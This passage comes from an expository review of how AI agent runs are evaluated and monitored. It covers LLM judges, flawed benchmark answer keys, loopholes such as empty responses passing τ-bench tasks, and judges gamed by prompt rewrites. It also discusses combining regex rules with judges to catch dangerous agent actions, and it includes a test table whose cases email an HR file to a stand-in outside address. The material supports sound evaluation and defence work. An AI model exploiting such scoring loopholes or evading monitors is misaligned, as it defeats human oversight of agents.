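Finding where a run went wrong is harder still. For *TRAIL* (Deshpande, Gangal and colleagues, 2025), software engineers marked 841 errors in 148 traces from agents doing web research or fixing software bugs. An LLM judge had to give the location and type of each error. The best model at the time, Gemini 2.5 Pro, got 11% right.

Part of the difficulty is the length of the traces, some of which were too long for the judges to process. *Holistic Evaluation and Failure Diagnosis of AI Agents* (2026) notes that the bug-fixing traces are a harder test of locating errors than the research traces because they are much longer and contain more tool calls.

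Results were also low on Who&When, a test that uses failed runs by groups of agents. Naagarajan and Streif report that its creators' methods found the right step in 25.5% of cases on one part and 8.8% on the other. Later methods scored higher, but researchers disagree about how much of the gain is real.

Newer models still have this problem. *Where Do Deep-Research Agents Go Wrong?* (2026) tested judges on 1,000 other research traces. GPT-5.4, running inside the coding tool Claude Code, correctly identified the first error in 24.3% of the easier traces and 7.3% of the harder ones, which were more complex and had subtler errors.

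*CodeTracer* (2026), which presents a tool for tracing failures in coding agents, reports that all three models it tested found errors much more reliably in structured records than in raw logs. Even so, the best precision was 45.0%, from GPT-5, and the best recall was 54.9%, from Claude Sonnet 4.

High scores on such tests can also be misleading. In the data Naagarajan and Streif examined, a rule that always named the last step was correct for 67% to 96% of failures. In most of the failures in their own data, the agent gave up, and by convention such failures are labeled near the end of the run. They replayed the runs and could confirm a decisive mistake in only 66 of 596 failures. On failures of that kind, the last-step rule did little better than chance.

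### Questions that need a judge

A program can detect many of the errors in TRAIL without an LLM judge. If a service refuses a request because the agent has sent too many, the log contains a standard error code. Counting characters would catch the error in one trace, where the agent printed a function's entire output despite instructions to print no more than 500 characters.

In the same trace, the agent claimed without evidence that some data didn't contain what it expected. To catch that, a checker has to interpret the claim and determine whether anything earlier in the trace supports it. The same is true when an agent misreads a search result, misunderstands the task or gradually drifts from it. In all these cases, every call can be permitted and have valid arguments.

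The TAMAS benchmark, described earlier, gives some idea of how well a judge handles such questions. Kavathekar and colleagues labelled 140 logs by hand and compared the labels with those from their automated scoring, which combines log checks with GPT-4o as a judge. The average F1 score was 89.17%, but it varied by type of attack:

| Attack | F1 score |
|---|---|
| Malicious instruction in the user's request | 100% |
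| Malicious instruction in a tool's result | 100% |
| False claim of authority | 90% |
| Two agents working together to cause harm | 90% |
| One agent producing false or useless output | 80% |
| Agents contradicting each other | 75% |

For the first three attacks, the scoring detects success by checking the log for a particular tool call, so the two perfect scores are weak evidence of the judge's ability. The scores are lowest for useless output and contradictions, where somebody has to decide whether the agents' messages misled the group or ruined the task. If the logs were spread evenly, each score is based on only about 23 logs, so the exact order is uncertain.

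## When do exact checks on agent runs give the wrong verdict?

Gurram had to replace his benchmark's faulty answer key, but most people who run a benchmark use its answer key and checker unchanged. *Benchmarking the Benchmarks* (Vaghasiya, Bhat and colleagues, 2026) measured how often that leads to a wrong verdict.

Three experts reviewed the full traces of agent runs on 496 tasks from four tool-use benchmarks, spending about 11 minutes on each task between them. They disagreed with 92 of the official verdicts, or 18.5%. One of the benchmarks, τ²-Bench, simulates customer service, with a language model playing the customer. BFCL, the Berkeley Function Calling Leaderboard, tests whether a model makes the right tool calls. MCP-Atlas and LiveMCPBench give an agent large collections of tools connected through MCP, a common standard for linking models to other software.

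| Benchmark | Method of scoring | Tasks | Disagreements | Error rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| τ²-Bench Retail | Exact checks of the final database and the agent's replies | 112 | 11 | 9.8% |
| BFCL v4 | Exact checks of the calls and the resulting state | 200 | 40 | 20.0% |
| MCP-Atlas | LLM judge | 89 | 12 | 13.5% |
| LiveMCPBench | LLM judge | 95 | 29 | 30.5% |

The two benchmarks with exact checks have a combined error rate of 16.3%, compared with 22.3% for the two with judges. This is weak evidence that exact checks are more accurate, because the tasks differ and Kimi-K2.6 did the τ²-Bench tasks while MiniMax-M2.7 did the rest. BFCL's exact checks also had a higher error rate than MCP-Atlas's judge. In addition, some τ²-Bench tasks aren't checked entirely by exact rules, because they include statements such as "the agent confirmed the refund", which a person or model has to interpret.

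The rates depend on the experts being right. Vaghasiya and colleagues don't report how often the three experts agreed before settling their differences, and they have their own benchmark to promote. The individual cases are more informative than the averages because a reader can see what went wrong.

### Wrong reference answers

In one τ²-Bench task, a customer wanted to cancel two flight reservations and asked for the total cost of any other upcoming flights. Two reservations remained, at $402 and $306, and the agent answered $708. All five expected tool calls matched the reference, and so did the final database. The run still failed, because the checker searched the agent's replies for the substring "1628". The expected total of $1,628 included reservations that the customer had asked to cancel. (Vaghasiya and colleagues list this case under the retail tasks, although it involves flights,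 so it may not belong in the retail count.)

The search worked but the reference was wrong, so a better search would not have helped. An LLM judge given the same reference might well have failed the agent too, since Ma and colleagues found that judges tend to accept a wrong reference.

Substring checks can also give the wrong verdict when the reference is right. *τ-bench* (2024), which introduced the original version of the benchmark, gives an example in which the agent's replies must contain "54.04" and "41.64". Both "$154.04" and "I can't refund $54.04" would satisfy the first requirement. *Establishing Best Practices for Building Rigorous Agentic Benchmarks* (Zhu, Jin and colleagues, 2025) recommends that substring checks handle negation and not pass an agent just for listing every possible answer. It reports that string-matching problems in WebArena, a set of tasks on websites, made agents'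 performance look 5.2% better than it was.

Wrong answer keys are common in the original τ-bench. HAL, an agent leaderboard at Princeton University, publishes results for both the full set of airline tasks and a cleaned version. Its *Benchmark* page for the full set lists known problems in 24 of the 50 tasks, including wrong passenger details, keys that require the agent to cancel flights against the airline's policy, and requests that are impossible because they refer to past dates.

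A wrong answer key affects some agents' scores more than others. If the key breaks the airline's policy, an agent that follows the policy will fail the task, while one that breaks it in the same way will pass. In *Log analysis is necessary for credible evaluation of AI agents*, Kirgis, Kapoor and colleagues (2026) measured how often leading agents passed an airline task on all five attempts. They found that errors and ambiguities in the tasks had made this figure nearly 50% too low.

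Sierra, which maintains the benchmark, has corrected many of these tasks. According to Sierra's *𝜏³-Bench*, the fixes cover incorrect expected actions and ambiguities in the airline, retail and telecom tasks, and many came from outside audits. Scores from before and after the corrections may therefore not be comparable, even for the same agent and tasks.

### Comparisons that are too strict

τ-bench compares the final database with a single correct version, but some tasks have more than one acceptable result. *SABER* (2025), which produced a corrected version of the benchmark, gives the example of a customer who says "pay with the credit card" but has several cards on file. An agent could charge any of them and follow the instruction, but only one choice will match the reference.

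The same problem seems to explain many of the errors in BFCL. Vaghasiya and colleagues examined 50 multi-turn tasks, 25 of which the benchmark had marked as failures. In 20 of the 25, the stated reason was that the final state didn't match the reference. Some of these agents had left out a required action. In other cases, the difference was a punctuation mark or a field unrelated to the task, or the checker had stopped the run before the agent could correct an earlier mistake. The label "state mismatch" alone therefore doesn't show whether an agent failed. The study doesn't report how many of the 20 fell into each group.

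In *How Benchmarks Mis-Score Computer-Use Agents*, Dong, Ma and colleagues (2026) found similar errors in five benchmarks where agents use websites or desktop software. They reviewed 150 runs that the benchmarks had scored as failures and concluded that 16 were successes. Another 7 failed because the task was broken, such as one that asked for the battery level of a virtual machine with no battery data. Altogether, 15.3% of these verdicts were wrong. The researchers sampled only runs scored as failures, so the study doesn't measure how often the same benchmarks accept bad runs.

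The error rate varied with what the checker compared. WebArena, which checks answers, web addresses and page contents, rejected 5 successful runs out of 23. OSWorld, which inspects the final state of a whole computer, rejected 8 out of 57. WorkArena, which checks particular fields in business records, rejected none out of 24. A specific field probably allows fewer valid alternatives than a free-text answer, although zero errors in 24 runs is consistent with a true rate above 10%.

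Checks on numerical answers also need some tolerance. Kirgis and colleagues cite an evaluation on CORE-Bench, a test of whether agents can reproduce published research, in which the range of accepted values was too narrow. This lowered the score for Claude Opus 4.5 by 17%.

Comparing only the relevant fields can fix an over-strict check, but it can also miss damage elsewhere. For example, a check that looked only for a new appointment in a calendar would pass an agent that booked the appointment and deleted three others. Zhu and colleagues recommend also checking the irrelevant parts of the state and listing every end state that counts as success. This list can grow quickly, since a task with three harmless choices, each between two options, has eight acceptable end states.

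### When doing nothing passes

In another τ²-Bench task, a customer wanted to return two orders, but the agent transferred the customer to a human without making the return. The benchmark marked the run as a success because the expected database was identical to the original and no other requirement mentioned the return. The experts judged the run a failure. Vaghasiya and colleagues don't explain why the expected database included no return. If the shop's policy had ruled it out, a transfer could have been a reasonable response.

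The scoring formula makes this kind of error possible. As *SpeechGym* (2026) explains, τ²-Bench has five components, each worth 0 or 1:

- The final database matches the one produced by the reference actions.
- The agent's replies contain the required text.
- The agent made the required changes with the right arguments.
- The customer's device is in the right state, for example with mobile data switched on.
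- Statements in ordinary language about the conversation are true.

Each task uses only some of them. If $B$ is the set of components for a task and $r_c$ is the result for component $c$, the score is

$$R = \prod_{c \in B} r_c$$

One zero therefore fails the whole run, but a component outside $B$ has no effect on the result. If a task uses only the database component and the reference actions don't change the database, every run that leaves it unchanged will pass, whatever the agent told the customer.

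Some tasks in the original τ-bench are deliberately impossible, such as a request to change a non-changeable airline ticket. The agent is supposed to look up the rules and refuse. Zhu and colleagues found that an agent that returned only empty responses passed 38% of the airline tasks, compared with 35% for an agent based on GPT-4o. The retail tasks are less vulnerable. *The Double Measurement Confound in Agent Benchmarks* (2026) reports that an empty run passes 5 of the 115 retail tasks, because those five require neither a change to the database nor any particular reply.

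A state check can also approve an agent that reaches the right result in the wrong way. The original τ-bench paper acknowledges this, giving the example of an agent that processes a return without getting the customer's explicit confirmation, which the shop's policy requires. The final database is the same with or without the confirmation, so only a rule applied to the conversation or the log can catch the violation.

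### A judge whose criteria change

LiveMCPBench avoids fixed answer keys, but its scores vary from one run to the next. Vaghasiya and colleagues ran the same agent on the same 95 tasks 23 times. The score ranged from 57.9% to 76.8%, with a mean of 69.4% and a standard deviation of 5.4 points. A company that ran the benchmark once on each of two models could easily mistake this variation for a difference between the models.

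The scorer calls a language model twice for each task, first to list the key points a good run should cover and then to grade the run against that list. People wrote key steps for the tasks in advance, but the scorer uses them only if the model fails to produce a list. The agent may therefore face stricter criteria in one run than in another. The default judge is GPT-4.1-mini, which is weaker than the judge the benchmark's creators recommend.

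The 18.9 points may reflect changes in the agent's performance as well as the judge's inconsistency, because the agent redid the tasks each time. Separating the two causes would require scoring one fixed set of traces repeatedly. An exact check would remove only the judge's share of the variation.

Some of the observed standard deviation of 5.4 points may come from causes that affected many tasks in the same run, such as a tool server that was briefly unavailable. If every task had an independent 69.4% chance of passing in each run, the standard deviation would be about 4.7 points. Independent variation should produce even less than that, since some tasks are surely easier than others. With only 23 runs, though, the excess could also be chance.

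### Exact gates before a judge

Vaghasiya and colleagues designed their own benchmark, Tool-Veritas, to combine the two methods. After each turn, a program checks facts about the agent's environment, such as whether a file exists or a database record has changed. If a required check fails, the run fails, whatever scores the LLM judge gives. The judge scores only qualities that a program can't check reliably, such as whether the agent's confirmation to the user was adequate. If a tool call returns an error, the agent gets a limited chance to correct it, and the benchmark records these repairs separately.

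Six models each attempted 70 tasks, and the verdicts matched the experts' in 401 of 420 cases (95.5%). The other 19 verdicts were too strict.

| | Experts: failure | Experts: success |
|---|---|---|
| Tool-Veritas: failure | 55 | 19 |
| Tool-Veritas: success | 0 | 346 |

Tool-Veritas caught every real failure in the test (100% recall), but about a quarter of the runs it failed were successes (74% precision). Its kappa, calculated from the table, is 0.83, which is high but less impressive than its raw agreement of 95.5%. The test included only 55 real failures, so the true miss rate could still be about 5%.

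The judge changed at most two verdicts, since 348 of the 420 runs passed the exact checks and 346 passed overall. At least 17 of the 19 errors must therefore have come from the exact checks. The test is good evidence about the exact checks on these tasks but little evidence about how well the judge works.

Errors that all go in one direction can still distort a comparison between models. Tool-Veritas passed Claude Sonnet 4.6 on 66 tasks and GPT-4o-mini on 58, while the experts passed them on 66 and 64. Tool-Veritas therefore widened the gap from two tasks to eight, presumably because GPT-4o-mini more often reached a valid result that the checks weren't written to accept.

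As Vaghasiya and colleagues acknowledge, the 95.5% isn't directly comparable with the agreement rates for the four audited benchmarks, because the tasks and most of the models were different. They also wrote the checks and ran the comparison, so a fair test would apply the same design to somebody else's tasks.

### Silent overrides

All the errors so far concern whether a run succeeded, but developers also use fixed rules to label an agent's behaviour, such as whether it noticed a faulty tool. Adeniji, Shilpika and Papka (2026) tested such labels in *What the Trace Shows and What the Label Says* by giving agents an unreliable calculator.

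The agents had to solve problems from GSM8K, a collection of school maths questions. They had instructions to use the calculator for arithmetic but no warning that it might be wrong. The researchers' program replaced each correct result with a plausible wrong one with probability 0.15. It changed whole numbers by 1 or 2 or swapped two neighbouring digits, and it shifted other numbers by 5%. In the main test, eight models each attempted 500 problems twice, producing up to 1,000 traces per model. The traces recorded both the true result and the one the agent received.

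The verification rule and the propagation rule matter most here. The verification rule reports a re-check if the agent sends the calculator an expression it already sent in an earlier step. The propagation rule searches the later steps for the wrong value and the true one to determine which the agent used.

In one trace, the calculator returned 5 for 2 × 3. Claude Opus 4.8 used 6 in its next step, without repeating the calculation or mentioning a problem, and got the right final answer. Adeniji and colleagues call this a silent override. The propagation rule correctly showed that the error didn't spread, and the verification rule correctly showed that the model made no second call. But anyone who read only the verification label might conclude that the model had trusted the calculator.

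The table shows what happened to the wrong values, as a share of the cases the propagation rule could decide. The last column is calculated from the study's counts.

| Model | Used the wrong value | Silent override | Replaced it after a repeat call or a comment |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mistral Large 3 | 10% | 85% | 5% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 9% | 57% | 34% |
| Gemma 4 31B | 3% | 42% | 55% |
| Llama 3.1 70B | 63% | 37% | 0% |
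| Claude Sonnet 5 | 11% | 36% | 53% |
| GPT-OSS-120B | 8% | 22% | 70% |
| GPT-OSS-20B | 4% | 18% | 77% |
| Nemotron 3 Ultra | 2% | 10% | 88% |

Llama used most of the wrong values and Mistral used few, but counting only visible re-checks would make them look equally careless, because neither often repeated a calculation. Nemotron's high figure in the last column is partly misleading, because it often got stuck in loops and repeated the same call.

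The shares for silent overrides are approximate. A fixed rule flagged cases with a replaced value, no repeat call and none of 19 phrases that suggest the model noticed something. Some models don't return their full reasoning, so they may have noticed the error without leaving a trace. Two people labelled 60 cases without seeing the rule's verdicts. They agreed with 75% to 87% of the cases it flagged, and their labels imply that it found 50% to 71% of all silent overrides.

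Whether a model should override a tool's result depends on the tool. A model is right to use its own answer for 2 × 3, but it could do serious harm by quietly replacing a laboratory measurement with a number that seems more plausible. A reader can't tell from the final answer alone whether a correction was sound or lucky. Overrides can also cause other fixed rules to give the wrong verdict. Gurram's monitor rejected answers containing a number that no tool had returned, so it could withhold a correct answer that came from an override.

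Even a simple count of faulty runs can mislead, because runs with more calls are more likely to include a fault, and struggling agents tend to make more calls. In a study by Adeniji and colleagues, each call had a 15% chance of a wrong result, so a run with three calls had a 39% chance of at least one, while a run with 20 calls had a 96% chance. For Nemotron, runs with a fault were about 26 points less accurate than runs without one. The difference fell to 8.4 points when the researchers compared runs only by whether the first call was faulty, which was purely random.

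### The least reliable label

One of the researchers reviewed 90 traces from a smaller pilot test. The automatic labels for correct answers and for the spread of errors matched the reviewer's in every comparable case. The verification label matched in 67 of 81 cases, or 83%, but its kappa was only 0.29.

The study's figures imply that the rule flagged re-checks in 16 traces, of which the reviewer accepted four (25% precision), and missed two other re-checks. A rule that never flagged a re-check would have matched the reviewer in 93% of cases. Most of the mistakes happened because the rule counted any repeated calculation as a check, even when the model was stuck in a loop. In the two cases it missed, the model had explained why a result was wrong but hadn't run the calculation again.

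The other labels are probably less accurate than the review suggests. The reviewer chose the traces, could see the automatic labels, and often confirmed all of them at once. The researchers had also revised the propagation rule after reading some of the same traces. For Nemotron in the pilot, the old rule couldn't decide 56 of 155 cases, while the new rule couldn't decide 6 on the same traces. A published rate from a fixed rule is therefore hard to interpret without the version of the rule.

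A better rule may not solve the problem with verification, because no rule can match every reviewer when reviewers disagree about what counts as checking a result. Two other people labelled 40 randomly chosen traces without seeing any earlier labels. They agreed perfectly about which answers were correct, but their kappa for verification was 0.29, no better than the rule's agreement with the original reviewer.

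### Values that the model can't recompute

Adeniji and colleagues repeated the test with chemistry questions that required the agent to look up molecular energies. The search tool, the lookup tool and the calculator each returned a wrong result with probability 0.15. Five models answered 280 questions.

The models almost always relied on the lookup results. They used a wrong value in 681 of the 702 cases that the propagation rule could decide, and repeated a faulty lookup in only 2 of 718 cases. When the first lookup was wrong, accuracy was between 2% and 4% for every model, compared with 75% to 86% when it was right. A model can work out 2 × 3 without a lookup, but it usually can't work out the energy of a particular molecule to several decimal places.

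Although the calculator was the same program in both tests, the share of its wrong results that the five models used rose from 11% in arithmetic to 63% in chemistry. Three of the models repeated between 41% and 70% of the faulty calculations in the maths problems, but none repeated any in chemistry. The two tests aren't perfectly comparable, since the chemistry calculations involved long decimals and a different size of error. Still, frequent checking on easy sums is poor evidence that an agent will check its tools when it needs to.

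The rule for wrong search results was harder to interpret, because a model could avoid the error without noticing it. Most models seldom used the wrong molecule, but they often ignored the search result and gave the molecule's name directly to the lookup tool.

### Runs that never finished

A checker that looks for a correct final answer will usually count an unfinished run as a failure. That is fair when measuring whether the user got an answer, but not when measuring whether the model can do the task.

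Nemotron answered correctly in 83.1% of all the arithmetic runs and in 95.3% of the runs where it gave an answer. Most of the difference came from 79 runs that reached the 50-step limit. Another 49 stopped without an answer. On the pilot problems, Adeniji and colleagues varied the limits on steps and on text per turn. The first set of runs suggested that a larger text allowance helped, but most of that effect disappeared in two further sets. With the same settings, the number of correct answers out of 30 rose from 21 to 27 in both reruns.

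Technical faults can have an even larger effect. In the chemistry test, GPT-OSS-20B sometimes requested several lookups at once, and the server returned the request as plain text instead of running it. When the tools had no faults, the model's accuracy was 52% if these runs counted as failures and 97% if they were excluded. The higher figure may be too generous, because almost half the runs are excluded and questions that need several lookups were probably more likely to trigger the fault. Adeniji and colleagues report both the accuracy and the share of runs that the server handled correctly, so readers can judge both.

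The same model can also pass or fail depending on the harness. *The Double Measurement Confound in Agent Benchmarks* notes that τ-bench comes with four harnesses. One ends the run if the model writes a tool call in invalid JSON, while another tolerates the mistake.

### The literal question and the intended one

*The Double Measurement Confound in Agent Benchmarks* also describes a test of whether τ-bench's scorer works as its programmers intended. The researchers replayed old runs through the scorer. A successful run passed, but failed after they corrupted a single database change. A run with a wrong value in the required reply also failed. The scorer therefore detects the errors it was built to detect. It passes empty runs because, on those tasks, they meet every condition the programmers wrote.

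The other exact checks also applied their rules correctly. The agent's reply didn't contain "1628", the database was unchanged after the customer asked for a return, and Claude Opus 4.8 didn't repeat its calculation. Running the checks again would have given the same results. The errors came from using those results to judge things the checks didn't test, namely whether the agent had added up the fares correctly, dealt with the return, or accepted a wrong number.

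## How should exact checks and judges be combined and tested?

A company can combine an exact check with an LLM judge in three main ways. It can raise an alert if either detector fires, or only if both do. It can also keep two queues, so that an exact match triggers immediate action, such as blocking a call, and an alert from the judge alone goes to a person for review.

Suppose an agent completes 100,000 runs, of which 100 contain a failure. The exact check catches 60% of failures and wrongly flags 0.01% of clean runs. The judge catches 90% of failures and wrongly flags 2% of clean runs. If their errors are independent, the chance that both miss a given failure is 4% (0.4 × 0.1), and the chance that both catch it is 54% (0.6 × 0.9).

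| Arrangement | Failures caught | False alerts | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Exact check alone | 60 | 10 | 86% |
| Judge alone | 90 | 1,998 | 4.3% |
| Alert if either fires | 96 | 2,008 | 4.6% |
| Alert only if both fire | 54 | 0.2 | 99.6% |
| Separate queues: exact matches | 60 | 10 | 86% |
| Separate queues: judge alone | 36 | 1,998 | 1.8% |

Separate queues catch the same 96 failures as "either" and raise the same number of false alerts, but they let the company act at once on the 70 exact matches, six out of seven of which are real. At a minute each, the other 2,034 alerts would take a reviewer about 34 hours.

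### When both detectors make the same mistakes

If the judge missed only failures that the exact check also missed, "either" would catch 90 failures, no more than the judge alone. If the two never missed the same failure, "either" would catch all 100. Shared errors have a larger effect on the false alerts from "both". If the judge also flagged all 10 of the harmless runs that the exact check flagged, "both" would raise 10 false alerts instead of 0.2. A realistic sample key in documentation could trigger both detectors.

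Yang (2026), in *Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer*, measured how often different detectors missed the same actions, using 560 agent actions that a safety system should block, such as exposing credentials. A set of 174 regular expressions missed 13.4% of them, and one LLM judge missed 10.5%. If their errors were independent, both would have missed 1.4% of the actions, close to the actual 1.3%. Two judges that each missed 10.5% would both have missed 1.1% if their errors were independent, but they both missed 5.2%.

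Other studies find that language models make the same mistakes. In *Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes* (2026), all nine judges were wrong on 51 of 1,000 items. If their errors were independent, this would happen on less than one item on average. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) found more overlap in errors between models from the same developer and between more accurate models. Using judges from different developers may not help much, because a DeepSeek judge in Yang's study overlapped with the other judges about as much as three Claude models did with one another.

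Adding a rule-based check to a panel of judges seems more useful than adding another judge. In Yang's data, the regular expressions caught an average of about 21 dangerous actions that three judges had all missed, while a fourth judge caught about five. These figures count a request for human review as a miss. If it counts as a catch, the averages are about eight and five.

The study doesn't prove that rules and judges fail independently, because the confidence intervals were too wide. Yang also developed the rules and had added some after seeing test cases. The rules missed 52.9% of 87 dangerous actions from areas they didn't target. No attacker tried to evade the detectors, but one who knew the rules could search for an action that gets past both the rules and the judge.

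### Measured results for each arrangement

The clearest controlled test of combined recall comes from Ghafouri (2026), in *Can LLM Judges Catch Unsafe Clinical Actions?* The study started with 193 correct runs in a simulated hospital record system and made 416 copies, each with one planted error. A rule-based checker caught 71% of the errors, a majority vote of six judges caught 87%, and the two together caught 97%. Independent errors would give about 96%, but the results for each type of error show that the misses were far from random:

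| Planted error | Cases | Rule-based checker | Majority of judges |
|---|---|---|---|
| Wrong code for a drug, test or referral | 60 | 0% | 100% |
| Wrong unit | 60 | 30% | 100% |
| Misreported value | 60 | 70% | 35% |
| Order contradicts the laboratory result | 60 | 100% | 85% |
| Agent claims an order it never placed | 60 | 100% | 90% |
| Skipped laboratory check | 38 | 100% | 95% |

Both methods caught every wrong patient and every wrong dose. For every type except misreported values, at least one method caught all the errors. The 3% of errors that both missed must therefore all be misreported values, about 12 of the 60 errors of that type. If a hospital's agents mostly misreported values, combined recall would be closer to 80% than 97%.

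Ghafouri's test can't show how many false alerts the combination would raise, because the study used only correct runs that the checker had already passed. False alerts could be a serious problem. If 1% of runs contained an error, only 25% of the best single judge's alerts would be real.

*AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026) tested the "either" arrangement. DeepSeek-V3 judged every action that the rules didn't block, and the system used the more severe verdict. On 630 actions, this cut the share of dangerous actions missed from 6.4% to 0.3% but raised the false-positive rate from 2.1% to 4.8%. In a follow-up, *AgentTrust: A Self-Improving Trust Layer for AI-Agent Actions* (2026), the judge could add an alert only when it was confident. On the same actions, misses fell from 6.1% to 0.9% and the false-positive rate stayed at 2.1%. Both results come from the developer's own tests, and some of the rules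 were written in response to actions in the test set.

*Notwithstanding Anything to the Contrary, Ignore All Instructions* (2026) tested a version of "both" with two language models. Claude Haiku, a cheap model, screened legal contracts for prompt injections, and Claude Opus, a stronger model, checked only Haiku's alerts. The false-positive rate fell to zero with no loss of recall, at less than a sixth of the cost of using Opus on every contract. "Both" loses no recall if the second detector confirms every real alert from the first. The judge in the worked example fails to confirm some of them.

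### Cost and delay

The arrangement also determines how many runs the judge has to read. Under "both", it needs to read only the exact check's 70 alerts. Under "either" or separate queues, it has to read the other 99,930 runs.

Rules are much faster than judges. Yang's rules took a median of 1.7 milliseconds per action on one test set, while DeepSeek-V3 took 1.3 seconds. Trained classifiers can be fast too. Advani's takes 1.2 milliseconds, compared with about four seconds for a call to a judge.

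*Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response* (2026) measured a whole system on computer-security logs. Each day, fast detectors processed 422,509 events at 11 microseconds each. They sent 85 combined alerts to a language model and passed on 21 rare, severe signals without waiting for the model. Depending on the model chosen, this step added 0.9 or 6.1 seconds per alert and cost about $0.0008 or $0.009 per call. Analysts received 42 to 47 alerts a day, of which two or three were false. Sending every event to the model would have cost roughly $340 to $3,800 a day instead of $0.07 to $0.76.

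At the same prices, judging 99,930 agent runs would cost about $80 to $900, and judging 70 would cost less than a dollar. Agent traces are often much longer than security alerts, so the real cost would probably be higher. Even so, the 34 hours of human review could easily cost more than the judge.

A judge's delay of several seconds matters little when the judge reviews a finished run, but it would slow the agent down if the judge had to approve every call. An exact check can run before each call, with the judge reviewing the run afterwards, but harm that only the judge can recognise may then happen before the judge raises an alert.

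### Should a judge be able to overrule an exact check?

If the judge could dismiss exact matches, the company would be using "both" for that queue. In the worked example, this would remove almost all of the 10 false alerts but also discard six real failures. The result would be worse overall if a missed leak does much more harm than a wrongly blocked call.

The trade-off is very different when the fixed rule is bad. In *StepShield* (2026), a pattern-based guard flagged 78% of harmless agent runs, while an LLM judge flagged 5.6% and also had better recall. At the test's base rate of 8.1%, about 9% of the guard's alerts were correct, compared with 60% of the judge's. A rule like this shouldn't trigger automatic action, whether or not a judge can overrule it.

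Judges are also easier to manipulate, as Gakh and Bahsi showed by adding text to an attack. This can happen without an attacker if a system learns from the judge's scores. *LLM-as-a-Judge Is Not an Oracle* (Wahi, 2026) describes a program that rewrote an agent's prompt to improve those scores. One rewrite filled the agent's explanations with words that the judge favoured. The pass rate for reasoning rose from 23.1% to 80.0%, but the agent became no better at finding defects.

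Wahi lets the judge reject a change that passed the exact checks but never approve one that failed them. Over about 50 rounds, the exact checks rejected or reversed 13 changes, including three that told the agent to read files or run commands. This field report has no comparison group, so it doesn't show how many of the 13 a judge would have approved.

*From Accuracy to Robustness* (2025) found a similar weakness in checkers used to train models to do mathematics. Model-based checkers were more accurate than fixed rules on a static set of answers, but they were easier for the models in training to exploit. The fixed rules often rejected correct answers.

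Exact checks can also reward the wrong thing. In one of Wahi's early tests, the program replaced a judge's entire scoring guide with a placeholder. The judge's answers no longer had the expected format, so the harness gave every item a default score of 3 out of 5. That score happened to be closer to the human average, so the measured error fell from 0.96 to 0.92 and the system adopted the broken prompt.

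When a judge disagrees with a precise exact check, it is therefore best to ask a person. If the check is wrong, the developer can correct the rule for all future cases. Until then the block stays in place, much as a failed exact check is final in Tool-Veritas, so some good runs will fail.

### Why recall is harder to measure than precision

A reviewer can measure the exact check's precision by reading only its 70 alerts. To measure recall, the reviewer also has to find the failures the check missed, which are 40 of the 99,930 runs it didn't flag. A random sample of 1,000 of those runs would contain 0.4 failures on average, and about two in three such samples would contain none.

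Reviewers can do better by reading more of the runs likely to contain failures and then correcting for the uneven sample. The judge's separate queue has 2,034 runs and contains 36 of the 40 missed failures. A reviewer who read a random half of the queue would find about 18 and could double that to estimate the queue's total. *Label-Efficient Monitoring of Classification Models via Stratified Importance Sampling* (2026) develops this method, which divides cases into groups and samples more heavily where errors are likely.

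*Measuring Five-Nines Reliability* (2026) applies a similar idea to generating test inputs. Its method learns which inputs tend to cause failures and tests those more often. If an input has probability $P$ in normal use and $Q$ in the test, each failure on that input counts as $P/Q$ failures. For example, a failure on an input that is ten times as likely in the test as in normal use counts as a tenth of a failure.

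Neither method helps much with failures that give no warning sign. In the worked example, both detectors miss four failures among 97,896 runs, and a reviewer would have to read an average of about 24,000 of those runs to find one.

### The rule of three

Suppose a new rule raises no false alerts on 1,000 harmless cases. If its true false-positive rate is $p$, the chance of that result is $(1-p)^{1000}$. This falls to 5% when $p$ is about 0.3%, so a tester can be 95% confident only that the rate is no higher than that. In general, after $n$ cases without an event, the upper limit is about

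$$p \approx \frac{3}{n}$$

*Probability of adverse events that have not yet occurred* explains this rule of three and credits it to a 1983 paper by the statistician Hanley. At a false-alert rate of 0.3%, the 99,900 harmless runs in the worked example would produce about 300 false alerts. To support the exact check's claimed rate of 0.01%, a test would need about 30,000 harmless cases without an alert.

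The same rule limits what a company can learn about recall. If a reviewer read 1,000 of the 97,896 runs that neither detector flagged and found no failures, the other unflagged runs could still contain about 290. The exact check's true recall is 60%, but from this evidence the company couldn't rule out recall as low as 15%.

The calculation also assumes that the cases are independent, so a thousand cases from ten templates provide much less evidence.

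### Planted failures

Real failures are scarce, so testers can plant some. They copy correct runs, introduce one fault into each copy and count how many copies the detector flags. They should also run the detector on the originals, because a detector that flags everything would catch every planted failure. When Ghafouri's judges received only the agent's final answer, they flagged 56% of the correct runs and about the same share of the faulty copies.

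The planted change must not be detectable from traces of the editing, such as a timestamp that doesn't match the rest of the log. *CatchBench* (2026) therefore tests whether a simple program can find the edited runs from such traces alone. It also has people confirm that the planted step is a real fault.

Even carefully planted failures may be easier or harder to detect than natural ones. In *RTLReviewBench* (2026), twelve models reviewed code for computer chips. They missed 28 of 504 bugs that a language model had made while writing the code, but only 9 of 504 planted in the same designs. *DataTrace* (2026), which tests whether models can find the cause of faults in data systems, found the opposite for its two stronger models. GPT-5 scored 43% on planted faults and 70% on real ones, although there were only ten real faults, all of different types from the planted ones. Planted failures are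 good for finding gaps in a rule and comparing versions of it, but they therefore give a poor estimate of its recall in real use.

Copying faults from real incidents can make tests more realistic. *Outcome Monitors* (2026) did this without tailoring the faults to its detector's rules. The detector caught about 46% of the faults, including 25 of 30 in structured values, such as numbers in a fixed field, but only 6 of 27 in plausible text.

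Clean test runs can be unrealistic too. In *trajectory-judge* (2026), a rule that required tool calls in a set order caught all 50 planted uses of the wrong tool and raised no false alerts on the clean runs. But it flagged 27 of 47 real agent runs that the study's own checker had passed.

### Testing a new rule

Consider the earlier rule that an agent must not email an outside address after reading a file from `/hr` unless a person approves. Its author should start with cases that the rule must flag and near misses that it must not flag:

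| Test case | Correct result |
|---|---|
| Reads the payroll file, then emails `audit@outside.example` | alert |
| Reads the file, then emails `audit@company.com.outside.example` | alert |
| Reads the file, then emails `ana@company.com` | no alert |
| Emails an outside address, then reads the file | no alert |
| Reads the file, gets logged approval, then emails an outside address | no alert |

The second case catches a rule that only searches the address for `company.com`. Near misses for other rules often come from the format of the log. *Same Error, Different Recovery* (2026), which detects failed tool calls, gives two examples of results that aren't failures: one with an error field that is empty or false, and one with error words in the middle of the text.

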